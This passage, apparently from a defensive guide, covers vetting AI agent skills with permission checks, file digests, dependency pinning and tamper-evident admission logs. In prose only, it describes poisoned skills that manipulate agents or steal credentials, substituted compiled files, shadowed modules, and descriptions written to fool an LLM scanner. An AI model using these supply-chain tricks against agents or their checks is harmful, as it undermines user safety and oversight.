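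The two lists can differ in two ways. For `pdf-processing`, they might look like this:

```
D = {read files, write files, use credentials}
A = {read files, write files, send data}

Used but not declared:  send data
Declared but not used:  use credentials
```

Undeclared network use is more worrying than an unused declaration, because whoever approved the skill based on its description didn't know about it. An unused declaration is often left over from a template, though it may give the skill more permissions than it needs.

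Wu and colleagues applied the method to 49,943 skills from ClawHub in early 2026 and found at least one mismatch in 80.0% of them. This figure excludes mismatches that fit none of the researchers' categories. Including those, and counting skills that share a name separately, raises the share to 91.0%.

Most mismatches appear to result from poor documentation. The researchers classified 163,754 of them and attributed 81.1% to developers' oversights and 18.9% to malicious intent. These figures are estimates, because fixed rules and a language model assigned the labels and nobody confirmed them by running the skills. The researchers predicted that a smaller share of the skills themselves, 8.8%, were malicious, which is also unconfirmed.

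The type of mismatch is more informative than its presence alone. The classifier identified malicious intent as the cause of 96% of mismatches involving instructions that manipulate the agent, compared with 56% of those involving credentials and 10% of those involving files. Reading a password, encoding text and contacting a server can each be harmless, but a script that does all three in sequence may be stealing the password. Wu and colleagues found sequences with apparent malicious intent in 2,490 skills (5.0%) and recommend a mandatory security review for those skills.

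They also tested whether the comparison helps detect malicious skills. On 906 skills, a language model that received both the files and the comparison caught 93% of the malicious ones and flagged 2.2% of the harmless ones. The same model without the comparison caught 69% and flagged 0.6%. But the researchers had generated most of the malicious skills themselves, using methods from earlier studies. On the 44 real ones, the model caught 28 with the comparison and 14 without it. The comparison therefore seems useful, although the 93% figure probably overstates how well it would work against real attackers.

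The method examines files without running them, so it can miss code that a script assembles as it runs. It also records that a skill sends data but not where, so it can't distinguish the skill's own service from an attacker's server. An attacker could avoid some mismatches by declaring network access. Unit 42's *Trust No Skill*, which comes from the same company as Wu and colleagues, acknowledges that an attacker who has read the research could also write a description to confuse the language model.

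### When the inspected source is not the code that runs

Reading a script's source is useful only if Python runs that source, and sometimes it doesn't. When one Python file imports another, Python may load a compiled copy stored in the same package instead of compiling the source again. This copy normally matches the source and saves time, but a skill's publisher can supply one that behaves differently.

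In October 2026, Liao and colleagues tested seven scanners on skills whose compiled file did not match the source. The scanners let through nearly all of these skills because none checked whether the compiled file came from the inspected source.

Their defence is a validator that traces which files the skill's instructions and scripts can cause Python to load. It compiles the inspected source with the matching version of Python and compares the result with the compiled file in the package. The comparison ignores filenames and line numbers, which can differ for innocent reasons, but includes the program's operations, names and constant values, so changing a single web address causes a mismatch. Rewording SKILL.md doesn't affect the result, because the comparison uses only code.

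In the test, the comparison caught all 100 substituted files and passed all 86 legitimate compiled files that came with their source. The validator blocked the other 14 legitimate files as a precaution because they had no source to rebuild from. The simpler alternatives did worse. Rejecting every compiled file caught all 100 substitutions but also rejected all 100 legitimate files. Checking only the identifying data at the start of each compiled file caught no substitutions.

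Rebuilding and comparing took about two milliseconds per package. A defender can also replace the supplied compiled files with ones built from the inspected source. Liao and colleagues tried this on 99 packages and removed the substituted code from all of them. Replacement seems better for most skills because it leaves the defender with a usable skill, but the log then has to record the rebuilt files.

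The perfect score applies to Python 3.11 and the file-loading methods the validator supports. The validator's comparison was inconclusive in 50 further cases, in which a skill used its own loading mechanism and supplied no source.

The full validator also looks for other attacks, including instructions hidden in text and images. In a test on 500 malicious and 200 harmless skills, it caught 92.8% of the malicious ones and flagged 10.0% of the harmless ones. It caught all of the compiled-file substitutions, which made up a fifth of the attacks, and between 89% and 94% of each of the other four kinds. Of the seven existing scanners, ExecScan caught the most malicious skills, at 70.0%, and flagged 37.5% of the harmless ones.

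### SkillFortify's guarantees and assumptions

A clean scan does not prove anything about a skill. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) presents SkillFortify, which is meant to prove the limited claim that a skill cannot exceed the permissions it declares.

The tool considers eight resources, including files, the network and the command shell. For each one, a skill can have one of four levels of access, in ascending order: none, read, write and admin. SkillFortify extracts commands, web addresses, environment variables and blocks of code from the skill, and each item sets a minimum level. A web address requires at least read access to the network, for example, and a shell command requires write access to the shell. The skill passes if, for every resource *r*,

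```
inferred level(r) ≤ declared level(r)
```

If `fill_form.py` contains a web address but the skill declares no network access, the inferred level is "read" and the declared level is "none", so the skill fails. Bhardwaj proves that if a skill passes for all eight resources, no run of it can exceed the declared levels.

The proof covers only the operations that SkillFortify extracts. If a script assembles a command while running, or reads a web address from another file, the tool may miss the operation, and the guarantee doesn't cover it. Nor does it cover what a language model does after reading the instructions. A separate theorem states that a skill will stay within its permissions at run time, but it depends on a runtime that checks every action. SkillFortify's first version has no such runtime, so the run-time protection is only a design. The threat model also assumes that no skill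 can escape the sandbox without a permission that allows it.

A skill can also do harm while staying within its declared permissions. For example, a skill that declares access to files and the network could steal files without exceeding either permission.

SkillFortify's detection results depend heavily on the test. On Bhardwaj's own benchmark of 540 generated skills, it caught 250 of the 270 malicious ones and flagged none of the harmless ones. Bhardwaj warns that the harmless skills were easy cases, because real skills routinely run programs and contact servers. Independent tests support this warning. In *MaliciousSkillBench*, SkillFortify caught 25.3% of the malicious skills and flagged 49.9% of the harmless ones, and Liao and colleagues measured rates of 8.6% and 50.0%. The theorem concerns permissions, not malice, so these results don't contradict it, but they are a strong reason not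 to admit skills on SkillFortify's verdict alone.

The tool also produces a lockfile containing the exact version and SHA-256 digest of each skill, the permissions allowed, the time and the tool's version. Bhardwaj's definition of the lockfile doesn't include an approver.

### Verification levels and proof bundles

An approval is usually just a yes or no, which hides how much evidence supports it. Metere proposes putting one of four verification levels in each skill's signed manifest. The level determines how often the runtime requests human approval before an irreversible action.

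| Level | Evidence | Actions that nobody can undo |
|---|---|---|
| Unverified | None | A person approves each one |
| Declared | An authorised signer has examined the skill and vouches that it stays within its declared permissions | The runtime approves those within the declared permissions and may ask a person about others |
| Tested | The skill has also passed a test under attack | As for "declared", but the runtime ends the session if the skill's effects don't correspond to the logged actions |
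| Formal | A program can check a proof that the skill stays within its declared permissions | As for "tested" |

Metere argues that people who receive too many approval requests start approving them without reading. A higher level for a skill reduces the number of requests, so the remaining ones may get more attention, but it also makes vetting mistakes more harmful. If a signer wrongly vouches for a skill that can send email, the runtime stops requesting approval for each message. To limit this risk, the runtime rejects a manifest whose signer lacks the authority to grant the stated level, and it never raises a skill's level during a session.

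*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) proposes three methods for reaching the "formal" level, which Metere originally described as an aspiration. Static analysis calculates the largest set of effects that the skill's scripts could have and compares it with the declared permissions. A type system labels each tool call that the language model makes with the permission it requires, and the runtime rejects calls that need an undeclared one. Bounded model checking examines every possible sequence of actions up to a fixed length. With ten declared permissions and one symbol for anything undeclared, there are 11⁸, or about 214 million, sequences of eight actions, which a computer can search in full.

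The results go into a signed proof bundle that accompanies the skill. When the runtime starts, it checks the proof again, so the user doesn't have to trust the person who produced it. The user still has to trust the checking program and its assumptions about how each programming language works.

Metere does not try to verify the language model. The proof allows the model to request any action and relies on the runtime to intercept every request. It covers only permissions, so a skill allowed to overwrite PDF files could still fill them with wrong figures. Metere has released an implementation and demonstrated it on a sample skill, but this is little evidence of how many ordinary skills could reach the formal level.

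### What to record about the vetting

Xiong and Zhang recommend that marketplaces show each scanner's version and scope, the version of the skill it examined, and the type and date of the review. An admission log needs the same details, together with the digests of the files inspected. An entry for `pdf-processing` might contain the following, with invented details:

```
Files inspected:  SHA-256 digests of all four files
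Scanner:          SkillSpector, pinned commit, static rules only
Blocking rule:    any high or critical finding
Finding:          high, fill_form.py line 42, reads an environment variable
Assessment:       false alarm, the variable names a temporary folder
Reviewer:         M. Okafor, read all four files
Sandbox run:      none
Date:             3 December 2026
```

The log entry should include the scanner's version and settings because they can change the result, as the tests of Cisco's scanner suggest. It should also include the blocking rule. Workloft's stricter rule blocked nine planted skills, while SkillSpector's default would have blocked six, so "passed SkillSpector" is ambiguous unless the entry specifies the rule. If researchers later discover that a scanner version misses an attack, the defender can search the log for every skill that passed that version and rescan them.

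The log should keep findings that the reviewer dismissed, with the reasons. SkillGate's log stores the model's label and confidence, the matched patterns, and the relevant text, which would let another person reconsider the decision. The entry should also list the checks nobody ran and the files a scanner couldn't read, since a blank field could look like a clean result.

The digests must come from the same copy that the scanner and the reviewer examined. Otherwise, the skill could change between the scan and the installation, as in Orca's test. The safest approach is to save one copy, compute its digests, examine it and install from it. If the installer has to download the skill again, the defender should compare the new files with the recorded digests before admitting them.

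## Choosing which files the record must cover

Before recording any digests, the defender has to find all the files that can affect what the skill does. The defender can't rely on SKILL.md to list them. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Versioned Transitive Dependency-Closure Binding and Operation-Time Effect Governance for Agent Skills*, examined 549 skills from public repositories of Anthropic and OpenAI. Of the 526 that contained files besides SKILL.md, only 21 gave the full path of every such file in SKILL.md. Many skills have several such files. Of the 163 skills in the library that *Scientific Agent Skills* describes, 154 include reference documents and 105 have a scripts folder, with a median of four script files.

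### A manifest for report-export

Take an invented skill, `report-export`, which turns a table of monthly figures into a formatted spreadsheet:

```
report-export/
├── SKILL.md             header and instructions
├── requirements.lock    exact versions of outside packages
└── scripts/
    ├── export.py        program that the agent runs
    └── format.py        fonts, column widths, number formats
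```

SKILL.md tells the agent to run `export.py`. That script imports `format.py`, which SKILL.md never mentions.

The defender starts by listing every file in the skill's folder, including hidden ones. The list must be the same on any computer that repeats the check, so the defender also needs rules for writing and ordering the paths. Each path is relative to the skill's folder, so the install location doesn't matter, and uses forward slashes even on Windows. The defender sorts the paths byte by byte, which places capital letters before lowercase ones and puts SKILL.md first. A program that ignored case would put SKILL.md last, and a digest of the list would differ even though nobody had changed the files.

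The next step is to compute the SHA-256 digest of each file's bytes, exactly as they are on disk. Git sometimes converts line endings when it copies text files to a Windows machine. This changes the bytes, so a team that uses both Windows and Mac should turn the conversion off for skills.

Finally, the defender hashes the list itself. The placeholders below stand for the digests:

```
SKILL.md             DIGEST-A
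requirements.lock    DIGEST-B
scripts/export.py    DIGEST-C
scripts/format.py    DIGEST-D

Package digest = SHA-256 of the four lines above = DIGEST-P
```

The package digest lets a checker compare the whole skill in one step. If it doesn't match, the separate lines show which file differs. The hashed text includes the paths because a list of digests alone might stay the same when someone renames a file.

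The programming language Go verifies downloaded modules in much the same way. It sorts the files, hashes each one and hashes the resulting list. Its digests begin with `h1:`, which identifies the method. An admission log should identify its method too, because two tools that put different separators between paths and digests will produce different package digests for the same folder.

### An edited script and an added file

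Suppose someone edits `format.py` after the approval so that it sends a copy of each report to an outside server. A new comparison gives this result:

```
                     Approved     Now
SKILL.md             DIGEST-A     DIGEST-A      match
requirements.lock    DIGEST-B     DIGEST-B      match
scripts/export.py    DIGEST-C     DIGEST-C      match
scripts/format.py    DIGEST-D     DIGEST-D2     mismatch
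Whole package        DIGEST-P     DIGEST-P2     mismatch
```

A defender who had recorded only the digest of SKILL.md would find no change. Also recording the digests of the scripts that SKILL.md mentions wouldn't help, because it mentions only `export.py`. Metere's signatures, for example, typically cover SKILL.md and "referenced scripts", so the signer of `report-export` would have to follow the references from one script to the next to include `format.py`.

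An attacker might instead leave all four files alone and add a fifth, `scripts/csv.py`. If `export.py` imports `csv`, Python will load the new file instead of the standard `csv` module, because Python looks in the script's own folder first.

A checker that only rehashes the files on the approved list would find four matches and miss the fifth file. To catch it, the checker has to list the folder again and compare the new list with the old one, which also reveals deleted files. The lockfile format proposed in samy-blog.pages.dev's *Your AI Agent's Plugins Are Not Verified. Seal Fixes That* treats both additions and removals as changes.

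### Links, permissions and generated files

A symbolic link is a folder entry that points to another path. If `format.py` were a link to a shared file elsewhere on the disk, a checker that recorded only the link's destination would not detect an edit to the shared file. One that listed only ordinary files, as the Unix command `find . -type f` does, would skip the link altogether.

Zhu and Wang either follow links to the real file or reject them, depending on the policy. For most skills, the simplest rule is probably to reject any link that leads outside the folder. For a link that stays inside, the manifest can record just the destination, because the target file already has its own line.

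On Mac and Linux, each file also has a setting that determines whether the system may run it as a program. The setting isn't part of the file's contents, so changing it doesn't affect the digest. It makes no difference if the agent runs `python scripts/export.py`, since Python only needs to read the file. It does matter if SKILL.md tells the agent to run the script directly. The manifest can include the type and setting of each file:

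```
file   not executable   SKILL.md             DIGEST-A
file   not executable   requirements.lock    DIGEST-B
file   executable       scripts/export.py    DIGEST-C
file   not executable   scripts/format.py    DIGEST-D

Package digest = SHA-256 of the four lines above = DIGEST-Q
```

Generated files can cause false alarms. When `export.py` first imports `format.py`, Python usually saves a compiled copy in a subfolder called `__pycache__`. The next check finds a file that nobody approved. Ignoring this subfolder would be unsafe because an attacker could put a substituted file there, like those that Liao and colleagues tested. A better solution is to have Python keep compiled copies outside the skill folder, in a folder that other programs can't write to. The finished spreadsheets should also be saved outside the skill folder. The skill folder can then be read-only, and any new file in it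 deserves attention.

Some skills include compiled programs or compressed archives. *Securing the AI Agent* (2026) recommends auditing these along with the readable files, since attackers may use them to avoid text inspection. A digest of an archive covers everything packed inside it, but not the copies that a script later unpacks. The script can unpack the archive again for each run, or the manifest can also list the unpacked files.

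### How often the approved file stays the same

Edits that do not change the main file are common in ordinary development. In *When the Approved File Is Unchanged*, Hossen (2026) measured how often they occur in deployment workflows and policies. A deployment workflow is a file of commands that put software into service. A reviewer may approve only this file, although one command in it can load dozens of others. Hossen's "authority set" is all the repository files that an approved run is configured to read, including the file shown to the approver.

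Finding these files took considerable work. Hossen searched GitHub for suitable workflows and policies, drafted authority sets for 30 of them, and checked every reference from one file to another. Only eight drafts needed no changes. Hossen corrected 12 and dropped 10, seven because the set could not be completed. The remaining 20 cases came from 20 repositories and had two to 44 files each, with a median of five.

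Hossen then went through 5,251 commits (saved snapshots of all the files in a repository), up to 500 from each repository. In 542 of them, a developer had changed at least one file in the authority set. In 296 of those (54.6%), the approved file stayed the same, so comparing its digest would have found no change. Hossen assumed no attacker was involved in any of these cases.

The share is fairly uncertain because a few repositories dominate the count. One accounts for 130 of the 296 commits, and without it the share falls to 43.6%. Resampling the repositories gives a 95% interval of 35.6% to 70.6%. The share also depends on the type of project. It was 145 of 184 for workflows that take their settings from separate deployment files. It was only one of 24 for programs that generate workflows, because developers usually changed the program and its output together.

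Hossen also tested such edits on local copies. In one repository, a few added lines gave a deployed role permission to write to a storage bucket. In another, a one-line edit reduced the number of human approvals required for high-risk changes from one to zero. Both times, the digest of the approved file still matched, but the digest of the whole authority set did not.

None of the 20 cases is a skill, so 54.6% isn't an estimate of how often scripts change behind an unchanged SKILL.md. But a skill has a similar structure: a short file leads to others that contain much of the functionality. Naming the files should be easier for a skill because most of them are in one folder.

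Even so, covering the skill's folder isn't always enough. In Zhu and Wang's sample, 67 of the 549 skills, all from OpenAI's repository, linked to files elsewhere in that repository. The audit didn't test whether agents open the linked files. If `report-export` relied on a style guide in a neighbouring folder, the defender could add the guide to the manifest or copy it into the skill before the review.

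### Letting the agent choose the files

In June 2026, Hossen asked two coding agents, OpenAI's Codex CLI and Anthropic's Claude Code, to choose the relevant files in a repository and compute one digest over them. Each agent attempted each of four tasks eight times. Hossen excluded two runs in which an agent had found an earlier list of files for the task, which left 62.

The agents computed the digest correctly in 61 of the 62 runs. In the other run, the agent put `./` in front of every path, so a checker using the agreed format would have rejected its digest.

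The choice of files was much less reliable. One task involved deploying with Terraform, a tool that creates cloud resources from text files. The agents chose five different sets of files over 16 runs. Codex chose the right 43 files every time. Claude Code chose four different sets in eight runs, and twice it left out all 42 Terraform files. The records from those two runs each had a correct digest of five files, so a checker that relied on either record would have accepted any change to the Terraform files.

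Across all four tasks, 59 of the 62 records covered every file that Hossen's audit identified in the agent's workspace. Of those 59, only 24 covered exactly those files, and the other 35 included extra ones. Extra files don't weaken the protection, but they cause unnecessary renewals.

Asking the agents whether one file was enough didn't help. In a separate test, they said they needed more than one file in 44 of the 48 runs where they did, and in 15 of the 16 runs where one was enough.

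The test used GPT-5.5 with reasoning turned off and Claude Sonnet 4.6, which are no longer leading models. Newer models may choose files more consistently, but Hossen's advice doesn't depend on the model. The checker should compute the digest itself and take the list of files from a source it can verify, such as a folder listing, a reviewed manifest or a tool's record of what it reads. For a skill, the checker can list the folder, and the agent can suggest files outside it for a person to confirm.

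### One file, a set, a manifest or a commit

The more files a record covers, the more often it needs approval. In Hossen's study, developers would have had to renew an approval covering only the main file after 246 of the 5,251 commits, and one covering the full authority set after 542, or about one commit in ten. An approval of a whole commit expires at the next commit, whatever that commit changes.

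| What the record fixes | Edit to `format.py` | New file in `scripts/` | Renewals over the 5,251 commits in Hossen's study |
|---|---|---|---|
| One file, such as SKILL.md | Missed | Missed | 246 |
| A chosen set of files | Found if the set includes the script | Found if the set includes a listing of the folder | 542 for the full authority set |
| A manifest | Found if the manifest lists the script and the checker hashes it again | Found if the checker lists the folder again | As for the set of files it lists |
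| A whole commit | Found | Found | After every commit |

If the rule for choosing files is too narrow, the record can miss a skill's scripts. GitHub's *Frontmatter Hash Specification*, for instance, follows a workflow's imports through every imported file but mainly collects the files' headers. A digest of headers alone would cover the name and description of `report-export` but neither of its scripts.

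People can read and review a manifest, but the checker has to verify it in two steps. It first compares the manifest's digest with the approved value, then hashes every listed file. If it stopped after the first step, it would miss an edit to `format.py`, because the edit doesn't change the manifest's text.

A whole commit is the safest choice if `report-export` has a repository to itself, since most commits there will concern the skill. It works less well in a shared repository, where a change to any one skill would end the approval of all the others. The OpenAI repository in Zhu and Wang's audit contained 530 skills.

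The commit also identifies files in a repository, which may differ from those on a user's disk. *Skills Are Not Islands* (Jia, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) cites a complaint from Claude Code users that skills circulate as loose copies without their original repository, path or version. For most skills, it therefore seems best to record the commit as the source and compare the files against a manifest of the whole folder.

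The defender should also keep a copy of the approved files. *Context Matters* (2026) reports that deleted and private repositories hampered data collection in a study of skill marketplaces, and it recommends immutable skill snapshots. Shen and colleagues' registry applies this principle by tying a skill's content, manifest and metadata to an identifier computed from the content, and an approved version stays fixed until a new audit begins.

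### Packages and other skills

The digest of `requirements.lock` covers the text of the lockfile, not the packages it names. It protects the packages indirectly if the lockfile gives a version and digest for each one and the installer rejects anything that doesn't match, as Python's pip can. If the lockfile contains only names, the installer can fetch different code over time while the lockfile's digest still matches.

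Many skills have no lockfile. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (Li, Guo and colleagues, 2026) studied all 48,682 skills on ClawHub in March 2026. Of the 4,259 that used npm, the main package manager for JavaScript, 69.6% had no lockfile, although over 90% of mainstream npm projects have one. For those skills, the package versions a user receives can depend on the day they install the skill.

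A script can also bypass the skill's lockfile. SafeDep explains that Python scripts can name the packages they need in a comment at the top. A tool called uv reads this comment and downloads the packages before running the script. If `export.py` had such a comment without version numbers, uv could load packages that `requirements.lock` doesn't list. The reviewer therefore has to look for package names inside the scripts and pin those packages too.

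A defender who pins a package still needs to check for security fixes from time to time and approve a new version when a fix matters. Li, Guo and colleagues found a known vulnerability in the packages of 49.6% of the skills whose package versions they could determine. Six months later, 88.7% of the vulnerabilities they could recheck were still there. Most of these vulnerabilities probably pose little danger, because an agent's input could reach the vulnerable code in only 3.0% of the affected skills.

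Skills may also rely on other skills. Jia and colleagues analysed 1.43 million skills and found that 15.48% depended on packages and 8.92% on other skills. More than 70% of the packages from each of npm and PyPI (the Python package index) came in through another skill, so a reviewer who read only the first skill would not have seen them. If `report-export` uses `pdf-processing`, the log entry for `report-export` should include the package digest of `pdf-processing`, which has its own manifest. The name alone would be ambiguous, since 58.73% of the skills shared a name with another skill.

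Zhu and Wang propose ClosureBound, which computes one digest over a skill and everything it depends on, including packages, tools, models and services. The digest also covers the connections between them, because a flat list would be the same whether a skill used a package directly or only through a sandboxed helper. Before an important action, the system works out the dependencies again, compares the new digest with the original and checks the action itself.

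Zhu and Wang tested weaker versions of ClosureBound on 32 unsafe cases. A version that checked only the skill's own identity allowed 26 of them, and one that recorded all the dependencies when the skill loaded allowed 20. The full system allowed none. They wrote the cases along with the system, so the results show what each check adds in those cases, not how well ClosureBound would stop real attacks. Its guarantee depends on the system finding every dependency, which is difficult when some appear only in prose.

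### Web pages and services

The digests also don't cover web pages, as AIR's test skill showed. If SKILL.md told the agent to follow the layout rules on a web page before each export, all four files would still match their digests after the page's owner rewrote the rules. Services have the same problem. Zhu and Wang note that an unchanged address doesn't prove the software behind it is unchanged.

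Estimates of how many skills depend on outside content vary because researchers have counted different things. The security company PromptArmor found an external package or web address in 52.1% of 1,046,413 skills, but this count includes links that may not affect the agent. Jia and colleagues found that 22.25% of skills depended on an external service. According to *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem* (2026), 17.7% of the skills on ClawHub fetched content from untrusted third parties, and 2.9% fetched and executed outside content while running.

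The 2.9% are the most worrying for a defender who relies on digests. The same pattern appeared in 21% of confirmed malicious skills, but it isn't always malicious. One skill, from moltbook.com, runs every few hours without supervision and has the agent fetch the skill files again whenever there is a new version.

Marketplace scanners often pass skills of this kind. Taneja and Weber (2026), in *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action*, examined 66,192 skill versions on ClawHub. They found 705 skills that every scanner had rated clean, even though the instructions included actions many organisations forbid, such as downloading a script and running it immediately. One publisher was responsible for 506 of these. They checked a sample of 100 by hand and found no sign of malicious intent among the correctly flagged skills. These skills may well have been harmless when they were scanned, but a clean rating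 doesn't cover a script the publisher uploads later.

Risky installation commands are usually in a skill's instructions, not in a separate installation script. Li, Guo and colleagues estimate that 910 skills on ClawHub had such a command in SKILL.md, compared with about 40 in an installer file. A defender who looks for downloads only in the code will therefore miss most of them.

The most reliable remedy is to remove the outside reference. The defender can save the layout rules as a file in the skill folder, change SKILL.md to point to it, and review and hash both files. The saved copy won't change when the original rules do, so someone has to check the originals for updates now and then.

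If a script has to download a file, the defender can put the file's expected digest in the script and have the script stop when the download doesn't match. For files in a code repository, an address that names a commit is safer than one that names a branch, because the owner can change what a branch points to.

SafeDep also recommends limiting the agent's internet access to the resources it needs. This would stop a changed page from sending the agent to an unapproved server for a program, but the owner of an approved server could still change what that server delivers.

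*Authoring Agent Skills* (2026) advises users to compare every external address in a skill with the skill's stated purpose before using it. The Hacker News recommends checking again whenever something changes. These reviews are useful, but a server can send different pages to a reviewer and an agent, so a harmless page in the reviewer's browser is weak evidence of what the agent received.

Some services have to remain outside the digest. If `report-export` looks up exchange rates, nobody can hash tomorrow's rates today. Zhu and Wang's approach is to keep an unverified dependency in the record and mark it as such, so that a later reader doesn't mistake an omission for a clean result. The file section of the log entry might then look like this:

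```
Skill:            report-export
Source:           repository address and commit
Path rules:       from the skill folder, forward slashes, byte order
Files:            four, listed with type, executable setting and digest
Package digest:   DIGEST-Q
Packages:         pinned by version and digest in requirements.lock
Other skills:     none
Web pages:        none
Services:         exchange rates, address recorded, responses not covered
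```

If a report later contains a wrong exchange rate and all the digests match, the last line gives an investigator a place to start.

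## Writing the log so that it cannot be quietly rewritten

If an attacker edits `format.py` in the approved `report-export` skill, the package digest changes from DIGEST-Q to DIGEST-Q2 and no longer matches the one in the admission log. But an attacker who can also edit the log can replace DIGEST-Q with DIGEST-Q2 there, and the check then passes.

A log is easy to rewrite unnoticed if it is an ordinary file on the computer where the skill runs, because any program with the user's permissions can usually change both the skill and the log. Reading the log carefully probably won't reveal the edit. *Hearsay* (Dai, Yang et al., 2026) asked 20 people to look for alterations in records of agents' work, with three people reading each record. By majority vote, the readers caught 37% of the altered records and wrongly flagged 10% of the unaltered ones. One language model caught 49% and wrongly flagged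 5%, while another caught 85% but wrongly flagged 42%. The log therefore needs a structure that lets a program detect edits.

### The full record for report-export

The full record contains the manifest's package digest, the details of the decision, and fields that protect the entry from later changes. The example below is invented.

| Field | Example entry | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| Event | Admission | Separates approvals from rejections and revocations |
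| Event ID | A random identifier | Stops a copied approval from counting as a new one |
| Skill and version | `report-export`, 1.0 | Lets people search the log |
| Source | Repository address and commit | Shows where to fetch a clean copy |
| Package digest | DIGEST-Q | Fixes the exact files and identifies the saved manifest |
| Not covered | Responses from the exchange-rate service | Warns that the digests say nothing about these |
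| Checks | SkillSpector, pinned commit, static rules, no high finding | Lets a colleague repeat the scan |
| Evidence | Digest of the full scan report | Reveals any later change to the report |
| Approver | M. Okafor, key 7 | Shows whom to ask and which key to check |
| Reason | The network call matches the description | Explains the decision |
| Scope | The finance team's computers | Limits where the approval applies |
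| Replaces | Nothing | Links an update to the earlier version |
| Time | 3 December 2026, 14:10 | Gives the approver's account of when it happened |
| Signature | Okafor's, over all the fields above | Reveals any later change to them |
| Entry number | 2 | Reveals gaps in the log |
| Previous digest | h1 | Links this entry to entry 1 |
| Entry digest | h2 | Covers this entry and, through h1, everything before it |

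Okafor signs the decision, and the log's software then adds the last three fields. *Identity-Bound Governance Under Execution Uncertainty* (Fernandez, 2026) uses a similar arrangement for deciding whether to restart a halted agent. The software supplies the evidence, a named person supplies the decision, reason and scope, and that person's signature covers both parts. The software can't forge an approval because it doesn't have the person's key.

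The event ID is needed because a copied signature is still valid. Fernandez submitted the same signed approval 1,000 times within its five-minute acceptance period. A verifier that checked only the signature and the time accepted all 1,000 copies, while one that also tracked event IDs accepted only the first. Without this check, an attacker might restore a revoked skill by appending its old approval to the log again.

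The evidence fields need their own protection. The skill store in *Learning by Doing* records the evaluator and its version, the test environment, the verdict and a reference to the evidence. It accepts results only from callers with access to that part of the store, because otherwise anyone could submit a passing result.

Like the manifest, each record needs a fixed field order and spacing so that every program computes the same digest. Fernandez uses a standard that sets both for JSON, a common text format for structured data.

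If outsiders can read the log, it may be better to identify each approver by key number and keep the matching names elsewhere. *Certifying That an Agent Skill Helps* advises against putting personal data in a permanent log because nobody can remove it later without breaking the record.

### Rejections, updates and revocations

Each later decision gets a new entry, and the old entries stay as they are. If someone edited entry 2 to read "revoked", an investigator could no longer tell that the skill had permission to run on the day of an incident.

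The log should include rejected submissions because publishers can try again. *Certifying That an Agent Skill Helps* simulated repeated attempts to pass its test of a skill's usefulness. A useless skill submitted up to 20 times had a 42.4% chance of passing if each submission counted as new. If the test became stricter with each attempt, the chance fell to 2.4%. A malicious publisher could likewise keep making small edits to a skill until it passes a security scanner. A reviewer who sees five earlier rejections would probably look more closely at the sixth version. This depends on recognising the submissions as related, which is difficult if the publisher opens a new account each time.

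An update is an admission that names the digest it replaces. It should also state whether the old version may still run, because some computers may not update for weeks. Sometimes two skills have to change together, such as when a new version of `report-export` needs a new version of `pdf-processing`. *Learning by Doing* shows the reviewer all the changes in such a group and then admits all of them or none.

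A revocation withdraws an earlier approval. In *AST02 — Supply Chain Compromise*, the security organisation OWASP recommends support for revoking one version by its digest, everything signed with a compromised key, or everything from one publisher. Revoking by digest is the narrowest option and leaves the publisher's other skills usable.

An approver's key may also need to be revoked. In Fernandez's system, approvals signed before the revocation remain valid but carry a note about it, and the verifier rejects later ones. Someone who stole the key could backdate a forged approval, so an entry's position in the log is better evidence of timing than the date its signer wrote.

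### Who can still alter each kind of log

| Type of log | How it works | Who can change an old entry unnoticed |
|---|---|---|
| Local file | A program adds lines to an ordinary file | Anyone who can write to the file |
| Hash chain | Each entry includes the digest of the entry before it | Anyone who can write to the file and recalculate the later digests, unless someone kept a copy of the latest digest elsewhere |
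| Keyed log | The software uses a secret key to calculate a check value for each entry | Anyone who can write to the file and has the key |
| Remote append-only storage | Another system accepts new entries but refuses changes to old ones | The people who run the storage, or someone who takes over their accounts |
| Transparency log | The operator publishes a digest of the whole log, and readers check that the log only grows | The operator, if readers don't compare the digests they receive |

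Where a log is stored can matter more than its format. *Auditable Agents* (2026) ranks logs on four levels, from weakest to strongest: no protection, append-only, hash-chained and signed. But an attacker who controls the user's computer can recalculate a hash chain stored there, and may have no way to change entries that another team keeps on its own append-only system. *Auditable Agents* found tamper-evident or cryptographically protected records in only two of the approaches it surveyed.

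Remote storage still accepts whatever the user's computer sends. An attacker on that computer can't change Okafor's approval but could add a false one, so the entries also need to be signed with a key the attacker doesn't have.

### A hash chain with three entries

A hash chain calculates each entry's digest from the previous digest and the current record:

```
h_i = H(h_(i-1) || record_i)
```

Here, H is SHA-256 and `||` means joining two pieces of data end to end. The first entry has no predecessor, so it uses a fixed starting value, h0, such as a row of zeros. Suppose the company rejected version 0.9 of `report-export`, admitted version 1.0, and revoked it after finding a flaw:

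```
record 1   rejection    report-export 0.9   DIGEST-N
record 2   admission    report-export 1.0   DIGEST-Q
record 3   revocation   report-export 1.0   DIGEST-Q

h1 = SHA-256(h0 || record 1)
h2 = SHA-256(h1 || record 2)
h3 = SHA-256(h2 || record 3)
```

An attacker now replaces DIGEST-Q with DIGEST-Q2 in record 2. The revocation names DIGEST-Q, so the altered skill would appear admitted and still valid. But when a checker recalculates the digest of entry 2, the result differs from the stored h2.

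The attacker can replace h2 with the new result. Entry 3 still contains the old h2 as its previous digest, so the mismatch moves there. The attacker can then correct that field and recalculate h3. This makes the chain consistent again, and it requires no secret because anyone can compute SHA-256.

A copy of the original h3, kept where the attacker can't change it, would reveal the substitution. Such a copy, called a checkpoint, should include the entry number so that a checker knows which digest to compare.

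| Edit | Chain alone | Chain and a saved copy of h3 |
|---|---|---|
| Change record 2 | Exposed at entry 2 | Exposed |
| Change record 2 and recalculate h2 | Exposed at entry 3 | Exposed |
| Delete entry 2 | Exposed at entry 3 | Exposed |
| Swap entries 1 and 2 | Exposed at the start | Exposed |
| Change record 2 and recalculate everything after it | Missed | Exposed |
| Cut off entry 3 | Missed | Exposed |
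| Add a forged entry 4 | Missed | Missed |

Cutting off the end of the log may be the simplest attack. If the attacker deletes entry 3, the remaining two entries form a valid chain with no gap in the numbering, and the log shows version 1.0 as approved. A checkpoint of the first three entries can't distinguish a forged entry 4 from a genuine one, so the signature has to reveal the forgery.

Certificate Transparency's *Verifiable data structures* gives the same warning about more elaborate logs. Someone can tamper with a record and recalculate the whole structure, and nobody can tell unless an auditor has old digests to compare.

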